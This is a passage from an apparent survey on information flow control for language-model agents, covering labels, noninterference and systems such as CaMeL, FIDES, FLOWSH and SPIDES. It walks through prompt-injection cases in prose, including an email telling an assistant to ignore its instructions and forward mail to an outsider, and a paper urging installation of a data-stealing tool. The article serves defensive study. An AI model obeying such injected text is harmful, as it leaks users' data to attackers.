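# How far information flow control can substitute for trusting a model's intentions

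## Labels, taint and noninterference in a language-model agent

Information flow control is a branch of computer security that governs where data may go after a program has read it. Such a system labels each piece of data with who may read it and whether its source is trusted, carries the labels through every computation, and blocks any action they forbid. The theory dates from the 1970s, when the standard example was a military computer that held both secret and unclassified files. Since 2023, researchers have been building information flow control into agents, which are language models that run in a loop, call tools such as a mailbox search or a file editor, and read what the tools return.

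The check matters for AI safety because it compares labels and ignores what the model was trying to do, so it treats a tool call from a well-meaning model the same as an identical call from a treacherous one. Researchers disagree about how much trust in a model's intentions it can replace. Some think the labels deal with hostile inputs but we must still trust the model itself. Others think strict enough enforcement can remove the need to trust the model at all. Still others hold that some harms depend on the model's intentions whatever the labels are. All three views use the same few concepts, most of which are older than language models.

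### The agent loop and prompt injection

An agent consists of a language model and a harness, the ordinary program that builds the model's prompts and runs its tools. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes how the two interact. The harness sends the model the user's request and a list of available tools. The model answers with either a final reply or a request to call one tool with certain arguments. The model only outputs text, so it cannot call the tool itself, and the harness decides whether to carry out the request. If the harness runs the tool, it appends the result to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model. This repeats until the model gives a final reply.

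The weakness lies in those appended results. Prompt injection is text placed in data an agent reads that gets the model to follow it as an instruction. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) calls it direct when the attacker controls part of the user's own input, and indirect when the attacker plants the text in a web page or document that the agent will later retrieve. An indirect attack needs no access to the agent. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) gives the example of an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub, a site where programmers share code. An attacker files an ordinary-looking report and adds a paragraph posing as a system message, which tells the agent to open a file of secrets and post the contents as a public comment. A person would see that paragraph as an odd footer, but the model receives the whole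 report as one continuous string, with no difference in syntax between the bug description and the attacker's instruction.

Developers can train models to resist such text, or filter it out beforehand. Both measures make a successful attack less likely, but neither rules one out. Information flow control instead acts between the model's request and the harness's execution of it.

### Labels and their order

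Most computer systems protect data with access control, which determines who may open a file. Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) point out in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* that this restricts the release of information but not its propagation. Once a program has opened the file, it can send the contents anywhere, by malice or by mistake. Keeping the data safe would require giving access only to programs that will not leak it, and access control cannot identify them.

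Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976) supplied the mathematics for specifying which information flows are allowed. Every object that can hold information has a security class, which later authors call a label. The relation A ⊑ B means that information in class A may flow into class B. The join of two classes, written A ⊔ B, is the class of anything computed from information in both.

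Denning argued that security labels must form a lattice, an ordered set in which any two elements have a least upper bound, or the flow rules would be inconsistent. Suppose the rules let a program store a + b in some place but forbade it to store a there. The program could set b to zero and store the sum, which would put a where the rules forbid it. The join of two labels, their least upper bound, must therefore be at least as restrictive as each of them. It should also be no more restrictive than that, so that wherever a and b may each go separately, their combination may go too. The order must be transitive as well, since otherwise two permitted flows could add up to a forbidden one. Transitivity lets an enforcer check operations one at a time, because any sequence of permitted steps is itself permitted.

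The smallest useful lattice has two points, public and secret, with public ⊑ secret. Public data may flow into secret places but not the reverse, and anything computed from both is secret.

A richer lattice uses sets of readers. Here a label is the list of people allowed to see the data, and a shorter list is a stricter label. The join is the intersection of the lists. Costa and colleagues work through a case with four users. If A, B and C may read document x, and B, C and D may read document y, then the readers of a text made from both are

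{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}.

User A drops out because A may not see y, and D drops out because D may not see x. *A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control* (Myers and Liskov, 1997) builds a system on this idea and adds a record of who owns each restriction. In that system, data may leave through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is on the data's list of permitted readers.

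The rules so far concern confidentiality. Integrity, which concerns whether data comes from trusted sources, follows the same rules in reverse. *SPA* (2026), a design for long-running agents, traces this observation to Biba's work in the 1970s. The order is trusted ⊑ untrusted, meaning that trusted data may flow into untrusted places, but untrusted data must stay out of places that need reliable input. Combining trusted data with any untrusted data makes the result untrusted. Agent designs usually pair the two kinds of label, so an internal company memo might be labelled "trusted; readable by staff" and a stranger's web page "untrusted; readable by anyone".

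### Noninterference, and two ways to leak

A rule for combining labels is a mechanism, and what it should achieve has to be defined separately. The usual definition is noninterference, from Goguen and Meseguer's *Security Policies and Security Models* (1982), which considers several users typing commands into a shared machine. A group of users G does not interfere with another group if, for every sequence of commands, deleting all of G's commands and running the machine again leaves the output seen by each member of the other group exactly the same.

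Later work on programs restates this with two runs that differ only in a secret. Let out(p, s) be everything an outside observer sees when a program runs on public input p and secret input s. The program is noninterfering if

out(p, s) = out(p, s′) for every p and every pair of secrets s and s′.

In the thought experiment for an agent, the agent does the same task twice with a mailbox that contains a letter about someone's salary, and only the salary figure changes between the runs. If outsiders can see any difference in what the agent sends, the salary has interfered. The same test works for integrity, except that the input that changes is an attacker's untrusted text, and the outputs that carry a trusted label should stay the same.

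Language models usually draw their words at random, so two runs may differ for reasons unrelated to the secret. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, therefore compare the probabilities of what the observer sees. Like most of the field, they also tolerate one leak by allowing a secret to affect whether the program finishes.

Noninterference is demanding because data can escape without anyone copying it. Consider this program, in which flag starts at 1:

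```
copy := secret
if secret = 0 then flag := 0
```

The first line is an explicit flow because it copies the secret into another variable. An enforcer that carries labels along as the program runs, a technique called taint tracking, will mark copy as secret. The second line writes only a constant, but anyone who reads flag afterwards knows whether the secret was zero. This is an implicit flow, in which the program's choice of action reveals the information. Denning noticed that it leaks even when the assignment never runs. If flag is still 1 at the end, the secret was not zero, but a monitor that tracks only executed instructions misses this because there was no assignment to track.

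An agent has the same problem whenever it chooses between tools. If it opens a certain public web page only when a confidential email mentions a merger, the page's owner can learn about the merger from the visit. Costa and colleagues settle for explicit secrecy, a weaker guarantee than noninterference that covers the first line of the program but not the second. Denning's model also excluded covert channels, such as a program's effect on how busy the machine is.

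### Why a language model is a hard case

In an ordinary program, labels can be fairly precise because a reader can see from the code which values go into each result. If a line computes z from x, z inherits the label of x, and a secret y elsewhere in memory doesn't affect that label.

A language model produces each token, a word or piece of a word, by a calculation over all the text in front of it. Any token of that text may affect any token of the answer, and no line of code shows which ones did. *GIF* (2026), a proposal for measuring how strongly each input sways a model's output, notes that classical flow control never specified how labels should pass through a neural computation that mixes instructions, private data and tool results. A summary of three emails might not depend on the third at all, but nobody can establish that by reading the summary.

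The safe assumption is that anything the model has read could have influenced its answer. Costa and colleagues therefore give every answer the join of the labels on everything the model has received so far in the conversation, including the tool descriptions. This join is called the context label. Each tool call the model requests inherits it, as do the arguments the model writes for the call. When the tool runs, its result takes the join of the labels on the call, the arguments and any stored data the tool read. The harness can compute all of these labels without interpreting the text.

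Denning's paper describes an early version of this idea, Rotenberg's Privacy Restriction Processor. This design from the early 1970s gave each running process the join of the classes of everything it had read and never lowered it. It had a well-known defect that Sabelfeld and Myers call label creep. Labels that can only rise end up higher than the results warrant, and for that reason the two judged run-time labelling "too restrictive to be generally useful". An agent's context label creeps in the same way. One untrusted web page at the start of a long conversation taints every later action, including those the page did not influence. Costa and colleagues cite one attempt to loosen this rule, a method that finds which messages influenced an answer and then regenerates the answer from those messages alone, so that it can carry a less restrictive label.

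Programmers can already try the strict version in GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes an experimental option that updates a context label after every tool result and attaches it to every tool call. The initial labels depend on where the data came from. GitHub's server marks files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. The system can therefore contain an injected instruction without anyone recognising it. This protection depends on the labels being right at the source. In Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, a tool that the developer forgets to label counts as trusted and public.

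### Two policies and two exceptions

Labels restrict an agent only when a policy refers to them. Costa and colleagues propose two basic policies, which *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) calls trusted action and permitted flow.

*Trusted action* allows a consequential tool call only if the model decided on it in a trusted context. The call and any argument that matters for safety, such as the recipient of a payment, must both be labeled "trusted". Whoever configures the harness decides which tools count as consequential. Deleting a file would count, for example, but looking something up in a closed company database might not.

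*Permitted flow* lets data leave through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is allowed to read the data. For an email, every recipient must be on the message body's reader list. This policy applies Myers and Liskov's rule for output channels to tool calls.

Permitted flow limits the damage from prompt injection. As Costa and colleagues acknowledge, it does not stop such attacks by itself, because an attacker can still steer the agent into any action that sends data only to people entitled to it. Trusted action stops the steering but does not restrict where the data goes.

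Strict enforcement of either policy would block much legitimate work, so practical systems allow exceptions. Declassification is a deliberate exception that lets secret data go to a reader its label excludes. In Myers and Liskov's system, an owner declassifies data by adding a name to the reader list, and when data derives from several owners, all of them must agree. Endorsement is the counterpart for integrity. Someone vouches for data from an untrusted source, and the harness then treats it as trusted.

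### An assistant that reads the project mail

Costa and colleagues illustrate the danger with an office assistant. A user asks it to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to the user's manager. One email contains a line telling the assistant to ignore its instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to an outside address.

To see what the labels do, suppose the user is Nora and the manager is Omar. The mailbox holds three relevant messages: a progress report from Lena, a budget note from Paul, which is the top email, and a message from an outsider with the injected line. Lena and Paul both copied Omar in. The harness trusts mail from colleagues and lets the people named on it read it. It treats mail from outside as untrusted, and as readable by anyone, since the company has no secrets in it. The context label then develops like this:

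| What the model reads | Label of the item | Context label afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| Nora's request and the harness's instructions | trusted; anyone | trusted; anyone |
| Lena's progress report | trusted; Lena, Nora, Omar | trusted; Lena, Nora, Omar |
| Paul's budget note | trusted; Nora, Omar, Paul | trusted; Nora, Omar |
| The outsider's email | untrusted; anyone | untrusted; Nora, Omar |

Paul's note removes Lena from the reader list because she isn't one of the note's permitted readers, and Lena's report excludes Paul for the same reason. The outsider's email doesn't change the reader list, but it flips the integrity label. The last line would be the same whatever order the agent read the documents in, because the result of a join doesn't depend on order.

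The result depends on the initial labelling rule. In a similar example from Microsoft, an email's readers are the people on it. Under that rule, the outsider's message would carry the list {Nora, outsider}, and the intersection would shrink to Nora alone. Permitted flow would then stop the summary from reaching Omar, so a stranger could block the agent's work just by writing to Nora.

The model has now read everything, with the labels shown in the table. Below are several tool calls it might request, with the result of applying each policy separately. The last row assumes that the outsider never wrote.

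| Requested call | Context label | Trusted action | Permitted flow |
|---|---|---|---|
| Send the summary to Omar, as Nora asked | untrusted; Nora, Omar | blocks | allows |
| Send Paul's note to the outsider, as the injected line demands | untrusted; Nora, Omar | blocks | blocks |
| Tell Omar, falsely, that Lena has resigned | untrusted; Nora, Omar | blocks | allows |
| Delete Paul's note | untrusted; Nora, Omar | blocks | has no bearing |
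| Send the summary to a client whom Nora never mentioned | trusted; Nora, Omar | allows | blocks |

The method's strength is that either policy blocks the theft in the second row, even if the injected line has fooled the model completely. Its drawback appears in the first row, where trusted action also blocks the errand Nora wanted done, because the harness cannot distinguish a summary the outsider influenced from one the outsider did not.

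A harness that requires every email to satisfy both policies blocks all five calls, including the honest one. Kolluri and colleagues choose a milder rule for tools that send data out, which requires only one of the two. Nora's summary then reaches Omar, because Omar may read everything in it, and Paul's note still stays inside the company. But the false story about Lena also gets through. Deletion is still blocked, because only the trusted action policy applies to consequential tools that send no data out.

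Nora could also endorse the outsider's email, which would keep the context trusted and let the summary pass both policies. If she endorsed it without noticing the injected line, the false story would pass both too. Sending the summary to a client would require declassification, and Lena and Paul would each have to consent under Myers and Liskov's rule.

Under the milder rule, though, the call in the last row needs nobody's consent, because the context is trusted. The rule is a form of robust declassification, which requires that untrusted data have no influence on a decision to release secrets, and here there was no untrusted data. Costa and colleagues reason that a release made in a trusted context "can be assumed to be intentional". They also grant that models misread their users and make needless tool calls even when every input is trusted. Nora did not intend to message the client. The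 model made that decision itself, and the integrity label can't show this because it records where data came from.

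## The view that inputs should be tracked and the model trusted

Most people who have built information flow control into working agents trust the model. They assume that Nora's assistant would serve her unless a stranger's email hijacked it, so their systems track what the model has read to try to make such a hijacking harmless.

### Trusted on clean input

Costa and colleagues set out the usual assumptions. They trust the user's messages, the tool descriptions, the model, and the system message, which holds the developer's standing instructions. The attacker cannot see or alter what passes between the harness and the model, but can plant text wherever the agent's tools fetch data and can observe the outward effects of some tool calls, such as a visit that shows up in a website's traffic figures. Kolluri and colleagues make the same assumptions and find them in two other designs from 2025,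 CaMeL and RTBAS. *SPA* places less trust in tools, since a malicious tool's description could mislead the model. But its threat model also excludes "alignment failures that arise independently of information flow".

People who hold this view trust the model only in a narrow sense. They assume that it does roughly what its user wants as long as everything it has read came from trusted sources. None of them claims that it can resist prompt injection, and some are prepared to assume that an attacker controls its output once it has read anything else. In *SPIDES*, a design for agents that operate a web browser, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) list the model and its provider as trusted. But they test the design against what they call a Byzantine adversary, who writes the model's output whenever untrusted text reaches the model.

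The case for drawing the line there rests mainly on how attackers behave. Suppose a model goes wrong on one request in a hundred. If these are the model's own mistakes, they are scattered, many do little damage, and developers can measure and reduce the rate. But an attacker who finds one message that works can send it to everyone who uses the agent. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, calls a 99 per cent detection rate a failing grade in application security, because the attacker's job is to find the other one per cent. On this reasoning, hostile input needs a check that never depends on the model's judgement, while ordinary testing and training can deal with the model's own mistakes.

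The system also has to turn "send the summary to my manager" into tool calls, and labels don't record what Nora meant by it. Only the model interprets her request. A harness that didn't rely on that interpretation too would have to get her intention some other way, most likely by asking her about every step, and delegating the email would then save her little or no effort.

### A planner that never reads the mail

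The designs derive from a blog post, *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023), which proposed splitting the assistant between two models. The planner model takes the user's request and can call tools, but never sees untrusted text. The quarantined model reads the untrusted text and has no tools, and Willison advises expecting it to go rogue at any moment. An ordinary program carries messages between them. Willison calls this program the controller, and it serves as the harness.

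Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The planner requests the email, and the harness stores it under a name such as $VAR1 and returns only that name. The planner then requests a summary of $VAR1. The harness puts the email's text into a prompt for the quarantined model and stores the output as $VAR2. Finally, the planner has the harness show $VAR2 to the user. An instruction hidden in the email can spoil the summary, but it never reaches a model that could act on it.

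Willison allowed the harness to pass the quarantined model's answer to the planner in only one case, when the model only has to sort a text into one of a few fixed categories. This is safe because the harness can check that the answer is one of those categories, and a category name can't contain an instruction.

The post calls its own solution "pretty bad". Any programming error that lets untrusted text reach the planner defeats the design. The user also reads what the quarantined model writes, so a planted instruction could make that model persuade the user to paste encoded private data into an attacker's website. The harness controls tool calls but can't stop the user from copying and pasting.

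### CaMeL and the altered address

The pattern has a further gap, because it protects the choice of steps but not the data that the steps use. Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind pointed this out in 2025 when they introduced CaMeL, and Willison retells their example. A user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, adding that the meeting notes contain Bob's address and the document's name. The planner sees only this request and arrives at a sensible plan, which one could write as follows:

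```
notes    := find_notes("last meeting")
address  := quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes)
title    := quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
document := fetch(title)
send(to = address, attachment = document)
```

An attacker who can edit the notes cannot add a step to the plan. But the quarantined model reads the notes, and a planted line can make it return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. The plan then runs as written and sends the document to the attacker.

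CaMeL closes this gap by tracking the data inside the plan. The planner writes the plan as a program in a restricted form of Python, and a custom interpreter runs it, recording which values each new value came from. Every value carries tags, called capabilities, that record its source and who may receive it. Before each tool call, the interpreter applies that tool's policy to the tags. In the example, the address comes from notes that an outsider could have edited. The mail tool's policy can therefore allow the message only if the user already trusts that address, and otherwise have the harness ask the user.

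*SPA* compares these tags with ordinary labels. Capabilities can express rules that a comparison of two labels cannot, but the guarantee then depends on each tool's policy being correct and complete. Willison notes that the design also helps privacy. The planner sees only the request, so the company that hosts it never receives the user's mail or files, and a smaller quarantined model could run on the user's own machine.

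Keeping the planner from seeing tool outputs also limits what CaMeL can do because, as Kolluri and colleagues observe, its plan cannot depend on those outputs. If a user says "complete the tasks due today in my to-do app", no planner can lay out the steps before it has seen the list.

### FIDES and selective hiding

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the planner sees a result and then picks the next step. It hides a result only when showing it would make the context label more restrictive. The planner sees data with label ℓ when ℓ ⊑ c, where c is the current context label. Otherwise the harness stores the data in a hidden variable and shows the planner the variable's name.

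The harness applies this test to each part of a structured result. For an email, it might pass the planner the date, which the mail server wrote, but replace the body with a variable name. In their experiments, Costa and colleagues hid only untrusted data and relied on the policies to protect confidentiality.

When the planner puts a variable's name into a tool call, the harness substitutes the variable's contents, and that argument carries its own label. A single call can therefore combine a trusted decision, a trusted recipient and an untrusted message. A policy can require only the decision and the recipient to be trusted.

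This allows Nora's errand, which the trusted action policy blocked when the model read everything directly. Under FIDES, the outsider's email stays in a variable. The planner asks a quarantined model to summarise the messages and sends the summary to Omar without reading it. The policy allows the call because the decision to send and the choice of Omar both come from a trusted context. The injected line can no longer redirect the mail, but it can still put a false story about Lena into the summary, because the quarantined model reads the outsider's email.

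The planner also has a tool that reveals a variable's contents and adds their label to the context label. The planner can therefore read any variable, but doing so can rule out later tool calls.

### Forward, summarise, schedule

Costa and colleagues use three requests to an office assistant to explain the purpose of each part of FIDES. They judge each solution by the informal rule that a tool call is safe if the model generated it only from trusted inputs.

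In the first task, the assistant must read the top three emails and send them to someone as a message on Slack, a workplace chat service. An agent without hidden variables breaks the rule because it has read three untrusted emails before it tries to send the message. With hidden variables, the planner fetches the emails, receives a variable name in place of their contents, and uses that name to send them without needing to read them.

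The second task is to send a summary of the emails. Copying is no longer enough, and inspecting the emails would taint the context before the planner could send anything. The planner passes the variable to a quarantined model with an instruction to summarise it, and receives the name of a second variable that holds the summary. An email could still instruct the quarantined model to produce an empty summary. A deployer can prevent this by requiring the message itself to be trusted, but that would block the task.

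Costa and colleagues call a task data independent if one fixed sequence of actions solves it whatever the stored data contains. Both tasks are data independent because each has a fixed sequence of tool calls and a fixed reply that solve it whatever the emails contain.

The third task fails that test. The assistant must check whether any of the emails asks for a meeting and, if so, put it in the calendar. The planner therefore needs one bit of information from the emails to decide whether to create an event or stop. It asks the quarantined model a yes-or-no question, and the harness restricts the output with constrained decoding, a technique that lets a model produce only text that fits a given format. The planner then inspects the answer. If it is yes, the planner has the quarantined model extract the date, time and participants into another hidden variable, and creates the event from that.

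Strictly, this breaks the rule as well, because the one-bit answer came from untrusted text. FIDES handles the exception by recording the type of a value in its label. The types have an order of their own,

yes-or-no ⊑ choice from a fixed list ⊑ free text,

which follows how much information each can carry. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit and a choice among k options at most log₂ k bits, while free text has no such limit. A label is now a pair of an ordinary security label and a type, and the join works on each half separately. A policy can then let an untrusted yes-or-no value influence a calendar entry while refusing an untrusted sentence. In effect this is a limited form of endorsement, in which the narrowness of the answer stands in for someone's having checked it.

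The reasoning holds for instructions, since one bit cannot contain a command, but it does not ensure that the bit is correct. An outsider can make the answer yes and also supply the meeting's details, and the policy already allows the assistant to act on both. The email could therefore put a fictitious meeting in Nora's calendar, although it could not make the assistant delete her files.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and chat tasks with planted attacks. Using OpenAI's GPT-4o, they counted 152 successful attacks on an undefended agent. FIDES with its policy checks switched off let 21 through, because the planner sometimes inspected a variable and read the attack. With the checks on, none got through. But the attacks followed a fixed template, so the test did not measure how well a more inventive attacker would do. The later systems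 replaced such templates with the Byzantine adversary, so their results do not depend on the model's ability to resist attacks.

### A planner that knows the rules

In the original FIDES, the planner is not given the policies the harness enforces, and it sometimes taints its context unnecessarily. Kolluri and colleagues built a successor, PRUDENTIA, that keeps the same enforcement but gives the planner the label of its context and the policy on each tool. Before revealing a variable, the planner must call a planning tool and state why it needs the contents and which tool calls it plans to make next.

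PRUDENTIA's planner can also ask the user to endorse a piece of untrusted data. If a harmless email lists ten tasks, the user can endorse it once instead of approving ten separate calls. Kolluri and colleagues considered offering declassification in the same way but decided against it, because they judged that whether a secret may go to a new reader depends too much on the context for a blanket permission.

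The clearest benefit of trusting the model is that a cooperative planner can use its knowledge of the rules to find a way to do the task that satisfies them, so the user gets more done with fewer interruptions. The same knowledge would help a planner trying to get around the rules, but the threat model excludes such a planner.

### Why the guarantee stops at explicit secrecy

For confidentiality, Costa and colleagues prove explicit secrecy. Let d₁ be the data that the agent's tools can read and write at the start of a run, and let g be the combined effect of the tool calls in that run, seen as a function from the starting data to the final data. Write d₁ ≈ d₂ when two sets of data agree in all their public parts. The run satisfies explicit secrecy if

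g(d₁) ≈ g(d₂) for every d₂ with d₂ ≈ d₁.

The definition holds g fixed, so the calls that the agent made on d₁ are replayed on d₂. Under noninterference, the agent would start afresh on d₂ and might choose different calls.

Suppose the secret is a salary. If a tool call copied the salary file onto a public web page, a replay with a different salary would produce a different page, and the run would fail the test. But suppose the agent read the salary and then opened a public page about sports cars, when it would have opened one about bus passes if the salary were lower. The replay opens the sports car page whatever the salary is, so the run passes, even though the page's owner has learned something about the salary. Costa and colleagues acknowledge that someone who watches the sequence of calls can infer a limited amount of information. Their definition also leaves out timing and the length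 of network packets, and their proof treats the model as deterministic.

Costa and colleagues judge full noninterference too restrictive for agents. Anything the model reads may affect what it does next, so in practice, once a tool might have read something secret, noninterference would bar the agent from calling any tool with publicly visible effects. An assistant that had opened Nora's mailbox could not then look up a train time on the web. They point to earlier systems that also accepted a weaker guarantee, including web browsers and TaintDroid, which tracked private data through Android phones.

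The compromise is easier to accept if the model is honest. An agent would have to arrange its actions as a code to pass much information through its choice of them, and a model that serves its user has no reason to do that. *SPA* is stricter. Its planner writes the complete plan before any tool runs, so the harness can identify every branch and label whatever happens inside it according to the data the branch depends on. This covers implicit flows within the plan, but enforcement also prevents *SPA* from completing many tasks it otherwise could.

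### Releases in a trusted context

FIDES and its successors follow the milder, either-or rule when a tool sends data out. Zverev and colleagues include the rule's exception for trusted contexts in their guarantee for SPIDES, under which data can reach someone outside its set of permitted readers only if the user approves or untrusted content has not influenced the flow.

Microsoft has published a sample policy of this kind for messages on Teams, its workplace chat service. The policy first checks the context label and allows the message if the context is trusted. Otherwise it fetches the channel's members and checks them against the list of people who may read the message. If every member is on that list, the message goes out. If not, the harness asks the user and names the members who aren't on it.

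The exception depends heavily on the model's honesty and competence, as another example in the same Microsoft post shows. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered mail. One email, from Priya, previews the quarterly sales figures. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but has no right to see them yet. Alex is the only permitted reader of a reply based on both emails. Microsoft presents this as a leak that the labels catch, and the permitted-flow check does catch it. But if the harness treats mail from colleagues as trusted, as Nora's does, and applies the either-or rule, the context counts as trusted. The rule then allows the reply, and the figures go to Marco even though no one has attacked the system.

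Defenders of the rule can answer that people often share things with new readers, and that sharing is often the purpose of the request. If Nora does ask for a summary to go to a client, a harness that enforced permitted flow on its own would stop her assistant from doing as she asked. The rule can also be a setting. In *FLOWSH*, a command-line system from the same line of work, a deployer can switch off the exception for trusted contexts (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026). The harness then catches confidentiality violations caused by the model's own errors, but more approvals are needed and fewer tasks are completed.

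### From tool calls to the command line

Coding agents do much of their work through a shell, the program that runs typed commands. FIDES checks a tool call before it runs, which works when the tool does one known thing, such as sending an email. A shell command can download a script and run it, and nobody can tell from the command what the script will do. FLOWSH therefore runs the command in confinement, tracks what it reads, and controls what it can change.

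Kim and colleagues run each command in a sandbox, an isolated environment whose only links to the outside are files and network connections. A monitor in the operating system's kernel records each file that the command opens, and all network traffic passes through a proxy, a program that relays it and can refuse to. FLOWSH keeps a label for the command as it runs:

command label = context label ⊔ labels of hidden variables in the command ⊔ labels of files opened ⊔ labels of sites contacted.

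This tracking catches flows that the agent's context label would miss, because a program can read a file without showing it to the model. The tracking is conservative. FLOWSH counts opening a file for reading as reading all of it, and if the monitor loses a record, FLOWSH treats the command as if it could have read anything.

Files and network requests need different treatment because the harness can undo a change to a file but cannot recall a message it has sent. While the command runs, its file changes go into a temporary layer on top of the real files, where only that command can read them. When it finishes, FLOWSH compares the final command label with the policy for each changed file and applies the changes if they all comply. Otherwise, the user accepts or rejects the whole set, since applying only some of the changes might leave the files inconsistent. The proxy checks each network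 request before passing it on, and treats even a request to read a web page as a release of data, because the address can contain a secret.

FLOWSH then gives the command's label to every file the command created or changed, and stores these labels in a part of the file system that sandboxed commands cannot rewrite. The labels remain after the conversation ends and the computer restarts, so a poisoned file downloaded on Monday is still marked untrusted when a new session opens it on Thursday.

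Kim and colleagues describe an agent that must compare published papers with a confidential design document. One downloaded paper contains an instruction to install a comparison tool, which is actually an attacker's program that would send the design document to the attacker's server. With FLOWSH, the agent can search the web, download the papers and read the design document without interruption. It must stop for approval before installing and running the tool, because that would overwrite protected files and send out confidential data. In their evaluation policy, a command that has read untrusted data may write only to the working and temporary directories. Even there, some files stay protected because they contain code that will run later, such as scripts that a version control system runs automatically.

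In tests with GPT-6.2 Sol under the Byzantine adversary, with no one available to approve anything, FLOWSH stopped all 40 attacks that reached a model, while a permissive sandbox stopped none of 51. FLOWSH has to forbid whatever it cannot monitor. For example, a command cannot leave a server running in the background, because FLOWSH ends every process when the command finishes.

### Labels inside a web page

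Web browsers separate sites with the same-origin policy, which limits how code from one site can interact with another site's data. Zverev and colleagues argue that restoring this separation for agents would protect users too little and also obstruct them. It would not stop an agent from posting a customer's account details as a public review on the same shop's website, because the data crosses no boundary between sites. It would obstruct a user who wants laptop specifications from several shops collected in a note-taking app, because that task requires moving data between sites.

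A single web page can also need several labels. A shop page, for example, can contain the shop's own price, a stranger's review and the customer's saved card number. SPIDES relies on the site's operator to mark in the page's code which parts the operator vouches for and which sites may receive each private item. The user keeps a list of sites whose operators they trust to do this, and SPIDES treats everything on other sites as untrusted and public.

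The planner then receives an outline of the page that includes the price, with variable names in place of the review and the card number. SPIDES hides an item if the item is untrusted and the context is still trusted, or if someone allowed to read the context is not allowed to read the item. If the planner inspects the card number, only the user and the shop may then read the context, and the review stays hidden.

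Clicks are as hard to judge as shell commands, because a click might follow a link or delete an account. SPIDES therefore classifies clicks, navigation and form submissions by site, on the assumption that the user has accounts only on the listed sites. On those sites, any of these actions could be taken in the user's name, so they all need a trusted context. On other sites, they count only as sending data, and the either-or rule applies. The harness always blocks tools that run arbitrary code in the page.

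Zverev and colleagues built a miniature web of 28 sites and tried 56 attacks with five models. SPIDES blocked all of them under the Byzantine adversary. Between 53 and 73 per cent succeeded, depending on the model, against a defence based on the same-origin policy. They labelled the sites themselves, whereas real operators would have to label their own sites and update the labels as their pages change. Because the labels name whole sites as readers, SPIDES cannot distinguish a private message to a friend from one to a stranger on the same social network. If the user lists a dishonest site, its operator can mark an attack as trusted.

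### What Microsoft has released

SPIDES and FLOWSH are research prototypes, but parts of FIDES are in products. In May 2026 Microsoft announced that it had added FIDES to Agent Framework, from version 1.3.0, as an experimental feature. Developers switch it on with a configuration object. By default, it hides untrusted tool results and sends them to a quarantined model, which answers single questions and cannot hold a longer exchange. Developers can have FIDES block a forbidden call, ask the user, or track labels without blocking, which lets them see what enforcement would do before they rely on it.

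Missing labels remain a weak point. Microsoft's May announcement treated unlabelled tools as trusted, but its documentation for the feature treats their output as untrusted and public by default. This is safer when a developer forgets to label a tool that reads web pages, but it doesn't protect an unlabelled payroll database, whose contents would still count as public. The documentation covers only the Python version of the framework, and Microsoft promises one for .NET, its own programming platform.

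So far, the experimental option in GitHub Copilot CLI enforces policies only for selected tools on GitHub's server. To support other servers, Microsoft has released a gateway that sits between an agent and its tools and adds the labels. It works over the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting models to tools. For each new tool, someone has to describe the structure of its results, write a function that labels them, and write or choose a policy. Microsoft plans to propose a standard format for labels and policies to the protocol's developers, so that the people who run a data source could label it themselves.

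## The view that enforcement can leave the model untrusted

Some researchers treat the planner as a possible attacker. They want guarantees that hold even if someone trained Nora's assistant to steal from her. Fokou (2026), in *PARALLAX*, assumes an agent whose safety training and refusals may all have failed, and asks what the rest of the system can still prevent. On this view, the model should stay outside the trusted base, which is everything that must be correct for a guarantee to hold.

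### The argument for a boundary outside the model

Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, start from the fact that a model receives instructions and retrieved documents as one string. The markers that separate them are also tokens, which an attacker can copy. The model therefore has no reliable evidence of where a passage came from, and Bhattarai and Vu argue that training cannot supply it. Their first theorem states that any learned separation of commands from data has a non-zero probability of letting some attacker's text through.

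That conclusion is weak, because a non-zero probability can be tiny, and they offer only a sketch of a proof. They also accept that training makes attacks succeed less often, but they want a guarantee, and point out that other kinds of computing get one from the architecture. A processor decides whether it may execute bytes in memory by looking up the permissions for that region, not by judging the bytes themselves. A database can avoid injected commands by receiving the query and the user's data separately.

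The argument applies equally to a model with perfect intentions, which would want to obey its user but could not verify which instructions came from the user. Bhattarai and Vu therefore separate alignment, which concerns what a model wants to do, from authorisation, which concerns what it may do, and think the two need different solutions.

For authorisation they propose a gate. The model picks an action from a finite list and fills in the parameters, and an ordinary program then computes

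σ(action, parameters, context) = allow or deny,

where the context includes the user's identity and the labels on the data. Suppose hidden text in a PDF persuades the model to email the user's private login key to a stranger. The model proposes the email, and the gate refuses it because the message contains confidential data that nobody has declassified. Bhattarai and Vu state a theorem about this gate. If σ is correct and deterministic, uses no language model, and checks every action, then nothing the model outputs can bring about an action that σ denies. They limit the claim to authorisation, since a model that may send email can still send a harmful one.

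The theorem follows almost directly from its assumptions. The hard part is knowing that the message contains the key after a program has encoded the key, split it up or made a decision that depends on it.

Fokou also puts a validator between the model and its tools, and tests it by leaving out the model and sending harmful tool calls straight to the validator. This "assume-compromise" test means the model's own good behaviour cannot explain a good result. The default configuration blocked 98.9 per cent of 280 such attacks. But some of the validator's checks use trained classifiers or another language model, so this is a measured success rate and not a proof.

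### A leak in the branch not taken

Garby and colleagues set out to prove something stronger, and they begin with a hole in CaMeL. CaMeL blocks an agent from emailing an outsider inside a branch that depends on a customer's balance. A slightly longer program gets around the check:

```
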